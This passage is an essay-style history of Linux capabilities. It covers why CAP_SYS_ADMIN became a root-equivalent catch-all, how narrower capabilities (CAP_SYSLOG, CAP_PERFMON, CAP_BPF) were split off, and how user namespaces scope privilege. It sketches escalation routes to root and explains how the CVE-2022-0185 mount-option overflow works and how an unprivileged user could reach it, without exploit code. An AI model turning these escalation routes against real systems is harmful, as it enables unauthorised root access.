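Linux 3.2 used capabilities in 1,167 places. CAP_SYS_ADMIN accounted for 451 of these, or 39%, in 229 files throughout the kernel. CAP_NET_ADMIN came second with 395, all in networking code. The other 34 capabilities accounted for the remaining 321.

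Kerrisk considered whether repetition had inflated the figure. Many device drivers perform similar administrative functions, and some kernel code exists in a separate version for each type of processor. He therefore counted again without drivers and without code for processors other than x86, the type in most PCs. He also made both counts for Linux 2.2, the first stable version with capabilities:

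| Code counted | CAP_SYS_ADMIN in Linux 2.2 | CAP_SYS_ADMIN in Linux 3.2 |
|---|---|---|
| All C files | 127 of 298 (43%) | 451 of 1,167 (39%) |
| Without drivers and non-x86 code | 23 of 147 (16%) | 167 of 552 (30%) |

CAP_SYS_ADMIN's share of all capability uses fell slightly across the whole source code. It was already large in 1999, when about four fifths of the uses were in drivers or in code for other processors. In the rest of the kernel, its share nearly doubled, because uses of CAP_SYS_ADMIN grew sevenfold while uses of all the other capabilities combined roughly tripled.

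Kerrisk's claim that developers increasingly fell back on CAP_SYS_ADMIN depends on the second row. That row probably better reflects how developers choose a capability, because someone writing a new driver can copy a check from an older one, while someone adding a feature elsewhere in the kernel more often has to make a new choice.

In an August 2019 update, which appears in LWN's *Comments on "CAP_SYS_ADMIN"*, Kerrisk reported that CAP_SYS_ADMIN's share had risen from under 39% in Linux 3.2 to just over 45% in Linux 5.2. He compared the new figure with the one for the whole source code, so it presumably includes drivers. If so, it is only slightly higher than the 1999 figure of 43%. He gave no figure without drivers, so it is unclear whether the share kept growing in the rest of the kernel.

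There seems to be no published count for a more recent kernel. Hallyn, who maintained the capability code, wrote in 2012 that he should repeat and expand the analysis, but no regular series appears to have followed. Kerrisk's method would also miss some checks in a current kernel. The header file by Morgan and Kjeldaas now contains small functions like this one:

```
static inline bool bpf_capable(void)
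{
    return capable(CAP_BPF) || capable(CAP_SYS_ADMIN);
}
```

Developers can call `bpf_capable()` from any number of C files. A process with CAP_SYS_ADMIN passes every such check, but searching those files for `CAP_SYS_ADMIN` finds nothing.

Even a complete count of the places where the kernel checks a capability would not measure how much power it grants. In Linux 3.2, only two places used CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, both in the same file, and only four used CAP_SYS_MODULE, yet either capability is enough to become root. Two checks can control access to every file on the machine if all file operations pass through them. Checks spread across fifty drivers may do nothing on a machine that has none of those devices.

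A count of source lines also doesn't show how many programs need the capability. Hasan and colleagues came closer by working out which system calls depend on each capability. They linked CAP_SYS_ADMIN to 28 calls, more than any other capability. One of these is `clone`, which programs commonly use to start processes and threads. It requires CAP_SYS_ADMIN only when a program asks for certain new namespaces, which most programs never do. If the researchers had looked only at the names of the calls, they would have concluded that every program in their study needed the capability, so they had to examine the arguments that programs pass to these calls.

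### How a developer ends up choosing it

The idea of a capability for miscellaneous operations came early. In December 2016, Kerrisk proposed manual-page advice on choosing capabilities, and Casey Schaufler replied by describing the POSIX group's work. Its members wanted capabilities to satisfy the least-privilege requirements in US government security evaluations. The evaluators examined how a system enforced its security policy, but some operations that needed privilege had nothing to do with that policy. Schaufler wrote that by far the easiest solution was to put them all under one capability and tell the evaluators that they did not have to look there.

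He later thought that the group should have divided these operations between two or three capabilities. It could have offset the increase by merging the capabilities for changing a file's owner, permissions and other attributes.

Schaufler's account helps explain why there was a catch-all. Kerrisk's explanation of its growth starts with a developer who has written a feature that ordinary users should not be able to use. The kernel has to check for a capability before it allows the operation, so the developer must either create a new capability or choose an existing one.

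Kernel developers discourage new capabilities because every addition gives administrators one more thing to understand, and the sets have room for only 64. Schaufler warned that there would be thousands if developers could create a capability for a single use, and said it was hard enough to get people to use a coarse set. The manual now describes CAP_SYS_PACCT as probably a mistake. It covers only the system call that turns process accounting on and off. Kerrisk's first example of such a mistake was CAP_WAKE_ALARM, which lets a program set an alarm that wakes a sleeping machine. Schaufler suggested that CAP_SYS_TIME could have covered it.

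In 2012 a developer had little help in choosing among the existing capabilities. The comments in the kernel's header file were supposed to list what each capability covered, but developers had updated them only sporadically. The manual page was a better guide, though also incomplete. Nobody coordinated the choices, and it could be hard to find someone to ask. Hallyn was responsible for capabilities, but his name did not appear in the kernel's MAINTAINERS file until just before the release of Linux 3.3 in March 2012.

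A developer in this position could at least be sure that system administrators would use the new feature, and CAP_SYS_ADMIN was on the list. Kerrisk thought the name was part of the problem. Most capabilities are named after a task, such as setting the time, but this one is named after a role. Almost anything that requires privilege is a job for an administrator, so a developer can't rule out the capability for any feature based on its name.

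The choice also looks safe, because if the developer picks a capability that is too powerful, few programs can use the feature and nobody reports a security hole. The problem appears later, when a program needs the feature and its administrator has to grant it all the other operations that the capability permits.

Kerrisk presented this as a hypothesis, based on his counts and a few conversations with developers. When he wrote, the test versions of Linux 3.3 had 13 new uses of capabilities, most of them CAP_SYS_ADMIN. But a developer may also choose the catch-all after careful thought. giraffedata, who had added privileged operations himself, wrote that he had always gone through the whole list of capabilities and almost never found a better fit. He regarded CAP_SYS_ADMIN as the category for things that did not merit their own capability.

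Better guidance would help developers who are confused by the list of capabilities, but not those who understand it and find no suitable category in it. A reader called ldo also doubted that coordination would be enough. In the 1980s he had seen similar overlaps and odd divisions in VMS, an operating system with a very similar set of privileges, which as far as he knew one organisation had designed centrally.

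Another reader, ballombe, suggested that developers invent a "virtual" capability for each new use and that the maintainer decide which real capability should cover it. This would coordinate the choice without lengthening the list that administrators see. One objection was that attaching several virtual capabilities to the same real one could create unexpected security holes. This can already happen whenever a developer reuses an existing capability, and under ballombe's plan one person would at least see all the decisions.

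The manual now includes the advice Kerrisk drafted, under which developers should prefer an existing capability to a new one. If a new feature would be useless without other privileged features, it should require the same capability as they do. Developers should avoid CAP_SYS_ADMIN unless the feature closely matches something it already covers. This last condition is weaker than it seems, because CAP_SYS_ADMIN covers so many operations that a developer can usually find one that looks similar.

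Schaufler disagreed with the warning against CAP_SYS_ADMIN. He thought the capability was the right choice for system administration, because a program that uses one administrative feature will very probably use others. This is plausible for a disk preparation tool, which might mount file systems, set quotas and turn on swap space. His argument does not justify putting the host name, the random number generator and the seccomp restrictions of other programs under the same capability. Kerrisk replied with a long list of what CAP_SYS_ADMIN allowed, and said that only a very broad definition of system administration would include it all. Neither had data on how often programs use several of these operations together.

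### The case for calling it the new root

Kerrisk called CAP_SYS_ADMIN "the new root" for two reasons. It allows so many operations that an attacker who holds it has several ways to obtain all the other capabilities. And because so many operations require it, a privileged program is more likely to receive it than any other capability. If both are true, dividing root's power achieves little for a typical privileged program, because an attacker who takes over the program can use CAP_SYS_ADMIN to obtain the other capabilities.

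The first claim is well supported. Spengler had already described routes through mounting file systems and inserting commands into an administrator's terminal. Hallyn pointed out that an attacker can also fill a file with deliberately malformed data and ask the kernel to mount it as a disk. The kernel's code for reading file systems may then crash or do something worse.

Arach, another LWN reader, raised the related concern that developers may be less careful with code that only privileged programs can reach, because they assume those programs are trustworthy. If so, each new feature under CAP_SYS_ADMIN may add to the poorly checked kernel code that programs with this capability can attack.

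Kerrisk supported the second claim with the number of checks in the kernel, which is only indirectly related to what programs need. On Spengler's machine, only one of nine services, `syslogd`, needed CAP_SYS_ADMIN, while eight needed CAP_SETUID. Hasan and colleagues also found that more programs kept CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE than CAP_SYS_ADMIN, although their tool assigned CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE too freely.

The same researchers found that distributions seldom attached capabilities to programs. They found only 29 programs that used capabilities among more than 59,000 packages in Ubuntu 21.10, released in October 2021. Of the 201 setuid programs in their study, only seven had switched to capabilities since Ubuntu 18.04, all of them network testing tools such as `ping` and `arping`. CAP_SYS_ADMIN therefore does not seem to be the capability that administrators grant most often to programs supplied with a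 distribution.

Granting CAP_SYS_ADMIN may be more common in containers. *KubeCap*, a study of Kubernetes, a system for running containers across many machines, reports that developers often grant CAP_SYS_ADMIN or full privilege to avoid working out which permission is missing. One configuration file it cites adds only CAP_SYS_ADMIN to a container called `cloudify-manager`. Of the 150 projects it surveyed, 112 did not set capabilities at all. It did not report how many of the other 38 granted CAP_SYS_ADMIN, so the survey does not show how common the practice is.

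CAP_SYS_ADMIN causes the problem Kerrisk described even if it is not the most common capability. A program that needs any one of its operations, however minor, must receive a root-equivalent capability unless kernel developers have also made that operation available under a narrower one.

### Why a catch-all might be safer

Kerrisk proposed, among other things, that developers move existing uses of CAP_SYS_ADMIN to other capabilities. Several readers doubted that this would help much. tialaramex argued that separating root-equivalent powers from one another adds almost no security, because forty capabilities that each lead to root are no better than one. An attacker who can become root by mounting a file system can do so whether the capability for mounting is called CAP_SYS_ADMIN or something narrower.

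kevinm went further and thought that all operations that can subvert the kernel should be under a single root-equivalent capability, whatever its name. JoeBuck suggested getting rid of root-equivalent capabilities altogether unless developers could close the routes to root. Programs that relied on them would run as root, and administrators would no longer have a false sense of security.

These arguments hold for attackers who can run any code. They are weaker for accidents, as giraffedata replied, and for bugs that give an attacker only partial control. For example, if CAP_SETUID and CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE were one capability, an attacker could trick the service that handles temporary files carelessly into overwriting the password file. Dividing root-equivalent powers therefore has some value, though much less than the idea of splitting root into small pieces suggests.

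tialaramex also pointed to a danger in moving operations out of the catch-all. A developer might put an operation under a narrower capability because it looks appropriate there, without noticing that it can lead to root. tialaramex considered this almost as bad as accidentally removing the check from something vital. Every program that already held the narrower capability would become root-equivalent, and its administrator would have no reason to suspect it. Kernel developers had recently made a similar mistake when they let processes with CAP_NET_ADMIN load modules unrelated to networking.

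Because lutchann ran containers, he did not want to search the source code of every new kernel to find out whether his containers were about to gain privileges. He preferred developers to put everything new under CAP_SYS_ADMIN, which people already knew to be equivalent to root. A container without that capability would then gain no power from an upgrade.

CAP_SYS_ADMIN is the safer place for an operation that nobody has examined closely. If developers put a dangerous operation under a narrow capability, programs that already hold that capability gain power they were never supposed to have, without anyone changing a setting. Putting a harmless operation under CAP_SYS_ADMIN leaves existing programs no worse off, but a program that needs the operation must then receive far too much power. An administrator can at least see this when granting the capability, and may decide to do without the feature.

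This defence assumes that people who grant CAP_SYS_ADMIN know how powerful it is. lutchann took that for granted, but another reader, cmccabe, thought that nearly every programmer knew what root was and that most would not recognise the name CAP_SYS_ADMIN. Kerrisk half-seriously suggested renaming it CAP_AS_GOOD_AS_ROOT. If developers grant it mainly to make an error message go away, as *KubeCap* describes, its innocuous name gives them little warning of its power.

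The defence also does not justify leaving harmless operations under CAP_SYS_ADMIN forever. tialaramex wanted developers to find operations that are useful on their own and do not lead to root on ordinary systems, and to move them out after a thorough examination. Hallyn's comments on mounting show that a single operation in the manual may have both safe and dangerous parts. Mounting over someone else's directory is dangerous because it can replace trusted programs, and mounting an untrusted disk image is dangerous because of bugs in the kernel's file-system code. But Hallyn also wrote that developers already understood how to let ordinary users perform many kinds of mount safely.

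In tialaramex's view, the catch-all was only a temporary place for new operations until someone examined them. In the seven years after that discussion, CAP_SYS_ADMIN's share of the kernel's capability checks rose.

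## Dividing a catch-all after programs depend on it

It is harder to move an operation out of CAP_SYS_ADMIN than to put one in, because programs that hold CAP_SYS_ADMIN may already rely on it for that operation. If a new kernel accepted only a narrower capability, those programs would stop working after an upgrade, and kernel developers try hard never to break existing programs. They therefore make the new check accept either capability:

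```
allowed = has(new capability) || has(CAP_SYS_ADMIN)
```

The symbol `||` means "or". A program that needs only this operation can now run with the narrow capability, and an attacker who takes it over usually gets much less. A program that keeps CAP_SYS_ADMIN works as before and is just as dangerous. An administrator who must grant CAP_SYS_ADMIN for mounting disks still cannot withhold the operation that now has its own capability. With one exception, which took 13 years, these divisions have not made CAP_SYS_ADMIN any smaller.

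### CAP_SYSLOG

The kernel keeps a log of its messages, which `dmesg` displays and `dmesg -c` displays and then clears. Containers share the host's kernel and therefore its log, so a program in a container with CAP_SYS_ADMIN could clear the host's messages. *Define CAP_SYSLOG* (Hallyn, 2010) proposed a separate capability for the privileged log operations. Whoever set up a container could then remove CAP_SYSLOG from its bounding set but leave CAP_SYS_ADMIN in it.

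Hallyn's patch required the new capability, CAP_SYSLOG, and no longer accepted CAP_SYS_ADMIN for access to the kernel log. He warned that a site running its logging service as an ordinary user with CAP_SYS_ADMIN would have to change its configuration. Kerrisk suggested accepting either capability, but Hallyn replied that a container with CAP_SYS_ADMIN could then still reach the log, which he wanted to prevent. Another developer, Matthew Helsley, suggested a period in which the kernel would warn about the old capability before refusing it. Hallyn preferred to warn and refuse at once, because he expected people to ignore a warning that had no consequences.

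CAP_SYSLOG arrived in Linux 2.6.37 with the strict check, which broke some programs. Torvalds explains in *cap_syslog* that these programs had dropped every capability except CAP_SYS_ADMIN, which they kept so they could read the log. A logging service that ran with all of root's capabilities also had CAP_SYSLOG, so it kept working. The change broke only programs written to follow the principle of least privilege as far as the kernel then allowed.

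In February 2011 Hallyn proposed accepting CAP_SYS_ADMIN for a few more releases. Another participant asked what anyone would gain from breaking the programs later instead of now, and Hallyn came to agree with him. Torvalds then changed the kernel to accept either CAP_SYS_ADMIN or the new capability, with a warning, until the old programs had caught up. Someone who wanted to grant another of CAP_SYS_ADMIN's powers without access to the log could split off that power too. This works only if developers have split off everything the program needs, and they have never done so for mounting.

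To stop the warning, Hallyn (2011) changed Ubuntu's package of `syslog-ng`, a logging service, to use CAP_SYSLOG where the kernel supported it.

Developers returned to the question in January 2024, when Meng (2024), in *[PATCH] cap_syslog*, proposed removing CAP_SYS_ADMIN from the check because old programs "may have had enough time" to change. Theodore Ts'o was not reassured and asked what testing supported this. He also saw little benefit, since an administrator who thinks CAP_SYS_ADMIN is too coarse can choose not to use it. That does not help someone who needs CAP_SYS_ADMIN for mounting. Petr Mladek, another kernel developer, supported the patch because letting several capabilities permit the same thing defeats the purpose of separating them.

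Steven Rostedt had suggested that developers settle such questions by removing the old check. They could restore it if anyone complained, and if nobody did, the removal had broken nothing.

Kees Cook searched for recent reports of the warning and found only an article that used it as an example. He asked Meng to start a few standard distributions and confirm that nothing triggered it. Meng replied that on Ubuntu 22.04 and Fedora 39 the warning was gone and CAP_SYS_ADMIN no longer gave access. Meng seems to have tested the modified kernel, which would not answer Cook's question because the patch had deleted the warning.

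Cook nevertheless accepted the patch into his branch on 1 February 2024, and Meng's commit *cap_syslog* (2024) removes eleven lines from the kernel. With this change, a container can have CAP_SYS_ADMIN without being able to clear the host's log through the system call, as Hallyn intended in 2010. The Linux man-pages still list the log operations under CAP_SYS_ADMIN.

### CAP_PERFMON

The `perf` tool measures where programs and the kernel spend their time. Many of its measurements required CAP_SYS_ADMIN until Linux 5.8, when Alexey Budankov of Intel moved performance monitoring into a separate capability, CAP_PERFMON. Budankov argues in *capabilities* that a monitoring process without the rest of CAP_SYS_ADMIN gives an attacker fewer privileges to exploit. The kernel still accepts CAP_SYS_ADMIN for these measurements too, so existing monitoring tools kept working.

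Budankov (2020), in *[PATCH 08/60] perf tools*, immediately changed `perf`'s checks to recognise the new capability, CAP_PERFMON, and its error messages to suggest it.

Carvalho de Melo (2020), in *[PATCH v8 00/12] Introduce CAP_PERFMON to secure system performance monitoring and observability*, ran `perf` as an ordinary user after attaching CAP_PERFMON, CAP_SYSLOG and CAP_SYS_PTRACE to the program file. Recording the whole machine with `perf record -a` worked, but the live display, `perf top`, failed with a permission error. CAP_SYS_PTRACE is root-equivalent, so an attacker who could run code in this copy of `perf` could still gain root's powers. An administrator who copied these settings would therefore have gained little security, though the trial doesn't show that `perf` needs all three capabilities for every measurement.

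CAP_PERFMON allows tracing that can read the kernel's memory, which may contain passwords and keys. In the 2019 discussions, Lutomirski imagined a finer division, which Starovoitov (2019) quotes in *[PATCH bpf-next] bpf, capabilities*. One capability would show which kernel functions ran and when, another would allow reading the kernel's data, and a third would allow tracing other users' processes. Lutomirski was unsure whether the existing code would let developers separate the first two. Linux ended up with one monitoring capability that covers both.

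### CAP_BPF

BPF lets a process load small programs into the Linux kernel, for example to filter network packets or record each call to a kernel function. Before a program runs, the kernel's verifier checks that it is safe. BPF programs keep their data in structures called maps, which they can share with ordinary processes. Ordinary users could load a few simple types of BPF program, but most other uses required CAP_SYS_ADMIN.

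Alexei Starovoitov, a BPF developer, proposed dividing this off in 2019. In his early design, Starovoitov (2019), in *[PATCH v2 bpf-next 1/3] capability*, let a process with CAP_BPF load every type of BPF program, while a separate CAP_TRACING covered some related features. The version that went into Linux 5.8 is stricter. Starovoitov (2020), in *[PATCH v6 bpf-next 1/3] bpf, capability*, requires a second capability for most uses, depending on what the BPF program will have access to:

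| Operation | Capabilities needed |
|---|---|
| Create most kinds of map | CAP_BPF |
| Load a tracing program | CAP_BPF and CAP_PERFMON |
| Load a networking program | CAP_BPF and CAP_NET_ADMIN |
| Load a networking program that also prints trace messages | CAP_BPF, CAP_NET_ADMIN and CAP_PERFMON |
| List all BPF objects on the machine and open them by number | CAP_SYS_ADMIN |
| Change an ordinary program's memory from a BPF program | CAP_SYS_ADMIN |
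| Run a BPF program on a network card | CAP_SYS_ADMIN |

CAP_SYS_ADMIN still suffices for the BPF part of every row. The IEEE group had tried to keep capabilities from granting new powers in combination, but here the developers deliberately required combinations. A process with CAP_BPF needs another capability to control network traffic or read kernel memory.

Much of the security benefit comes from still requiring CAP_SYS_ADMIN to open BPF objects by number. Suppose two services both hold CAP_BPF and CAP_NET_ADMIN, and one loads a firewall as a BPF program. The kernel gives that service a file descriptor for the program's attachment to the network. The other service cannot remove the firewall unless the first one passes it the descriptor. If both services had CAP_SYS_ADMIN, either could open the other's BPF objects by number and interfere with them, perhaps by accident.

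Because the descriptor works as an object capability, Starovoitov (2020), in *[PATCH v7 bpf-next 0/3] Introduce CAP_BPF*, moves nearly all the permission checks to the point when a process loads the program. He compares this to opening a file, after which the kernel does not check permissions again on each read. Previously, a process needed CAP_SYS_ADMIN to load a networking program and CAP_NET_ADMIN to attach it, but a process could get around the check on attaching in several ways.

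He also wanted to prevent networking programs loaded without CAP_PERFMON from reading arbitrary kernel memory, which CAP_SYS_ADMIN had permitted. He intended the new capability to help people who test the verifier by feeding it random programs, too. They had been running their tests without privilege, so they could not reach the code for the verifier's more advanced features.

CAP_BPF is far safer than CAP_SYS_ADMIN, which includes it, but a little riskier than Starovoitov's phrase "harmless on its own" suggests. He noted that a process can load many programs at once and make the verifier use so much memory that the whole system slows down. CAP_BPF also lets testers reach more of the verifier's code, and attackers can use the same access to look for bugs.

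He also warned administrators against attaching CAP_BPF and CAP_PERFMON to the files of tracing tools such as `bpftrace`, because anyone who ran the tool could then read the kernel's secrets. The capabilities should go to particular users, who can pass them to the tool through the inheritable or ambient set. `bpftrace` resembles `rm` more than `ping`, since what it does depends on the person running it.

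The same series of patches switched the kernel's own BPF tests to CAP_BPF and CAP_PERFMON. A program can give up CAP_SYS_ADMIN only if it uses no operations that still require it, so a tool that inspects everyone's BPF programs has to keep it.

### BPF tokens

The kernel did not accept a CAP_BPF that was valid only inside a user namespace, such as a container's, because BPF programs run in the kernel that all the containers on a machine share. Nakryiko (2024), in *[PATCH v2 bpf-next 00/30] BPF token*, added a way to delegate part of BPF to a container.

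The privileged program that sets up the container first mounts a BPF file system for it, with options that list what the container may do. *Privilege delegation using BPF Token*, from Canonical's documentation for the container manager LXD, gives an example with four options. The first, `delegate_cmds=map_create:prog_load`, lets the container create maps and load programs. The other three limit it to one type of map and one type of program, and let it attach programs only where they see incoming network traffic for a group of processes.

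A program in the container then asks the kernel for a token based on this mount. It needs CAP_BPF within the container's user namespace to do so, as Nakryiko explains in *[PATCH v2 bpf-next 03/30] bpf*. The token is a file descriptor that the program passes with its later BPF requests. The kernel checks these requests against the token instead of the program's own privileges.

BPF tokens divide privilege much more finely than CAP_BPF does, and they need no new capability numbers because mount options set the limits. Their drawback is that, as with other file descriptors, a process can pass them to another process. When Nakryiko proposed the first version, he wanted tokens to stay inside the container, but LWN pointed out that a process could still deliberately send one to a process outside it. LWN reported that in a later version he seemed to have met most of the objections. LWN's index lists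 the tokens under Linux 6.9, and at least one container manager, LXD, supports them.

### CAP_CHECKPOINT_RESTORE

CRIU (Checkpoint/Restore In Userspace) saves a running process to disk and later resumes it from the same point, perhaps on another machine. Java developers wanted to use it to skip their programs' slow startup. Operators of large scientific computers wanted to save long calculations that ordinary users had started. Reber recalls in *capabilities* that people had asked for years whether CRIU could work without root, and that the usual answer was "almost".

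The main obstacle was the process ID, which must stay the same when a process is restored because the process or its children may have stored it. Choosing the ID of a new process required CAP_SYS_ADMIN, so a tool that needed this small power had to hold a capability equivalent to root. Linux 5.9 made CAP_CHECKPOINT_RESTORE sufficient for choosing the ID and for reading certain links that show which files a process has mapped into memory.

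Reber's first version was named CAP_RESTORE. Horn (2020), in *[PATCH] capabilities*, replied that when a process is restored into its own PID namespace, which has a separate set of process IDs, its old ID is guaranteed to be free. On a shared system, another process may already have that ID. User namespaces already let users restore processes without root, but not every CRIU user could set up such an environment.

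CRIU's developers prepared an unprivileged mode while the kernel change was still under discussion. But the new capability did not cover everything they needed. In December 2023 Reber, in *[PATCH v2] tty*, proposed extending it to a terminal setting that CRIU changes when it restores a program started from a shell.

Developers can rarely foresee every operation that a tool will need, so a narrow capability tends to grow. Each addition risks giving new power to programs that already hold the capability, the danger tialaramex described, though the risk is probably small for a terminal setting.

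### How many capabilities are enough

Each capability takes one bit in a 64-bit set, and with 41 in use there is room for 23 more. Kernel developers added 14 between 1999 and 2020. At that rate the remaining bits would last more than thirty years.

Developers cannot reuse the bit of a capability that turns out to be a mistake. Ts'o mentioned in the 2024 discussion that program files and configurations may contain old sets in which that bit is still on. If developers gave the bit a new meaning, those programs would receive a privilege that nobody had meant to grant them. CAP_SYS_PACCT, which covers a single system call, will therefore probably keep its bit permanently.

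In his 2016 draft of the manual's advice, Kerrisk gave the 64-bit limit as the reason to prefer existing capabilities over new ones. Schaufler replied that the real problem was managing so many capabilities, and he considered the need for such advice sufficient evidence of that. He also had Kerrisk remove a statement that capabilities divide root into "small" pieces, because small pieces would mean many capabilities.

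Schaufler's standard example was DG/UX, Data General's version of Unix, which ended up with 330 capabilities. An administrator granting privileges there has to know what each capability does and which ones a program needs. The program won't work if it gets too few, and any it doesn't need are extra privileges for an attacker. Schaufler (2007) thought that about 20 would be enough, though he called this a matter of taste. He saw the main purpose of capabilities as separating privilege from user ID 0, and thought even a single "CAP_GODLIKE" would be better than giving root all privilege all the time.

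Albert Cahalan had disagreed in 2000, when he called the system with 330 capabilities better designed and complained that Linux had "no safe way to 'split' a capability", so it was stuck with its existing divisions. Schaufler replied that in his experience hundreds of capabilities could not be good design. Cahalan was partly right about splitting. The "or" lets developers add alternatives to a capability that is too broad without breaking programs, but they can seldom reduce the original's power.

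That seems like a reason to start with narrower capabilities than Schaufler wanted. But developers who start too narrowly can't remove surplus capabilities either. The manual's compromise is to group features that are useless without each other, and to make any new capability broad enough to cover related features later.

### Should setting the host name have its own capability?

Setting the machine's host name still requires CAP_SYS_ADMIN, although it is a minor power compared with mounting a file system. A separate capability would cover only two system calls, which set the host name and the domain name. It would be almost as narrow as CAP_SYS_PACCT, so under the manual's advice developers should not create it.

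They could instead let CAP_NET_ADMIN permit setting the host name as well. Programs that configure a machine's network connection sometimes receive a host name from the network and set it, so the two tasks often go together. But setting a host name is useful without configuring a network, and most programs that configure networks never change the name. It is therefore unclear whether the advice about features that are useless without each other applies here.

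If the operation that sets the host name were moved to CAP_NET_ADMIN, every program that already has that capability would also be able to change the name. This could matter for `sudo`, which can apply different rules on different machines according to their host names. If an organisation copies one file of rules to all its machines, a user who can rename her machine might obtain rights meant for another machine. Developers would have to look for such cases before making the change, and a program that only sets the host name would still have control over the network.

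CAP_BPF, CAP_PERFMON and CAP_CHECKPOINT_RESTORE each cover a group of related operations used by existing programs that people wanted to run without CAP_SYS_ADMIN. Setting the host name doesn't belong to such a group, and neither do many of the other operations that CAP_SYS_ADMIN permits. The manual's advice can keep new features out of the catch-all, but it does little for the small, unrelated operations already in it.

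An administrator can avoid the problem without a new capability by letting one trusted service set the hostname for other programs. systemd includes such a service, `systemd-hostnamed`, which checks whether the user making a request may change the hostname. The service still needs CAP_SYS_ADMIN, but the programs that send it requests do not.

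## User namespaces and containers

A program in a container may need to set a host name, mount a file system or configure a network, but only for that container. Linux's original capabilities could not be limited in this way. CAP_SYS_ADMIN let a process change the host name and the mounted file systems for the whole machine, because the machine had only one set of each. Kernel developers later let a group of processes have its own copy of such resources, called a namespace. They then needed a way to limit a capability to particular namespaces.

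### Root inside, an ordinary user outside

A user namespace has its own user IDs, group IDs and capabilities, according to the Linux man page *user_namespaces(7)*. A machine starts with one, the initial user namespace, and every other user namespace has a parent. Since Linux 3.8, released in 2013, unprivileged users have been able to create user namespaces.

Suppose that Alice, whose user ID is 1000, runs this command:

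```
unshare --user --map-root-user bash
```

It creates a user namespace, starts a shell in it and gives the kernel a one-line table of user IDs:

```
0 1000 1
```

The first number is an ID inside the namespace, the second is the matching ID outside, and the third is how many consecutive IDs the line covers. Alice's shell has user ID 0 inside the namespace but still has user ID 1000 outside it.

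The shell has all 41 capabilities in the new namespace and none in the old one. It keeps them when it executes another program because its user ID is 0 in the new namespace, so the usual `execve` rules for root apply.

Alice still cannot read `/etc/shadow`. The kernel translates her ID back to 1000 before checking it against the file's permissions. Her CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE doesn't help, because inside a user namespace it applies only to files whose owner and group both have IDs in that namespace, and her namespace's ID map doesn't include the machine's root user, who owns the file.

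Without privilege, Alice can map only her own ID. A container often needs more, because its web server and its database run as different users. The line `0 100000 65536` maps IDs 0 to 65535 inside the container to IDs 100000 to 165535 outside, which nobody else uses. Writing that line requires CAP_SETUID in the parent namespace, since Alice could otherwise map another user's ID and act as that user. Distributions supply a privileged helper, `newuidmap`, which writes the line for her after checking that the administrator has assigned her the range.

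### Which namespace the kernel checks

Kernel developers can write a permission check in two ways. `capable(CAP_SYS_ADMIN)` tests whether a process has the capability in the initial user namespace, and therefore over the whole system. `ns_capable(ns, CAP_SYS_ADMIN)` tests whether it has the capability in the user namespace `ns`. The developer passes the user namespace that owns the resource as `ns`.

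Other kinds of namespace hold the resources themselves. Kerrisk (2023), in *User Namespaces*, gives examples: a UTS namespace holds a host name, a mount namespace holds a set of mounts, and a network namespace holds routing tables and port numbers. Each belongs permanently to the user namespace of the process that created it. The kernel starts with that owner and works upwards:

```
start with the user namespace that owns the resource
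repeat:
    if the process is in this namespace:
        allow if the capability is in its effective set, else refuse
    if the process is in the parent namespace
       and its user created this namespace: allow
    if this is the initial namespace: refuse
    move to the parent namespace
```

A process with a capability in the initial user namespace also has it in every container. A process inside a container has no capabilities over the parent namespace or neighbouring containers. When a user creates a user namespace, their ordinary processes outside it have every capability in it, so the user can manage what runs there.

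### Setting the host name and setting the clock

Alice's shell has CAP_SYS_ADMIN, but she can't change the host name because her command created only a user namespace. The shell is still in the machine's UTS namespace. That namespace belongs to the initial user namespace, where she has no capabilities.

She can add `--uts` to the command to create a UTS namespace as well. The kernel creates the user namespace first, so the new UTS namespace belongs to it. Her process has CAP_SYS_ADMIN in that user namespace, so this time the kernel lets it change the hostname. Only processes in that UTS namespace see the new name.

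Containers share the host's system clock, because Linux time namespaces cover the clocks that count from startup but not the date and time of day. A process therefore needs CAP_SYS_TIME in the initial user namespace to set the system clock. Likewise, a process needs CAP_SYS_MODULE in the initial user namespace to load a kernel module, because all containers share one kernel.

| Operation | Capability | Where Alice needs it | Result |
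|---|---|---|---|
| Set the host name of her own UTS namespace | CAP_SYS_ADMIN | Her user namespace | Allowed |
| Set the machine's host name | CAP_SYS_ADMIN | The initial user namespace | Refused |
| Set the system clock | CAP_SYS_TIME | The initial user namespace | Refused |
| Load a kernel module | CAP_SYS_MODULE | The initial user namespace | Refused |

If Alice also creates a mount namespace, she can make a directory appear at another location and mount several kinds of file system, including temporary ones held in memory. She cannot mount a disk image directly, because the kernel code that reads it might mishandle malformed data, as Hallyn had warned. Anything she mounts over `/etc` is visible only to programs in her mount namespace, and the machine's setuid-root programs do not gain root there.

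Kernel developers separated the safer mounts from the dangerous ones without adding a capability, by changing in which user namespace the kernel checks for CAP_SYS_ADMIN. This also avoids the compatibility problem that made CAP_SYSLOG slow to separate, since a process with CAP_SYS_ADMIN in the initial namespace still passes every check.

### More kernel code within reach

These limits hold only if the kernel code that performs the operations is correct. Before user namespaces, a process needed real privilege to configure a firewall or mount a file system, so a bug in that code was of little use to an ordinary user. Now any user can create a namespace, receive every capability in it and run much of the same code. Hallyn (2024), in *[PATCH 0/3] Introduce user namespace capabilities*, calls user namespaces a great success because they give no privilege over the host's resources, but says the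 extra code they expose is the unaddressed issue.

For example, an attacker could use this to exploit CVE-2022-0185, a bug in the code that collects mount options in a 4,096-byte buffer. Before adding an option, the kernel compared its length with the remaining space, which it calculated as 4,096 − 2 − the number of bytes already used. With 4,095 bytes used, the result should have been −1, but the code used an unsigned integer, which cannot be negative, so the result became a very large positive number. Every further option then seemed to fit, and the kernel wrote past the end of the buffer.

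To reach this code, a process needed CAP_SYS_ADMIN in the user namespace that owned its mounts. Alice could have gained that capability with one command, then used the overflow to take control of the kernel and become root on the whole machine.

Biederman (2024), in *[PATCH 1/3] capabilities*, quotes a list that includes this bug and four others from 2022. Three of those four were in the kernel's firewall code, which a process can reach with CAP_NET_ADMIN in its own namespace. Eric Biederman, the main developer of user namespaces, has opposed several attempts to restrict them. He thought the seriousness of the problem was debatable, but agreed that for unprivileged users "the attack surface is undoubtedly enlarged".

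Turning off user namespaces also has a security drawback. Chromium, the open-source browser behind Chrome, uses them to sandbox the processes that handle web pages so they cannot reach the user's files. Without user namespaces, Chromium needs a setuid-root helper to set up the sandbox or has to run with a weaker one.

### The hook in Linux 6.1

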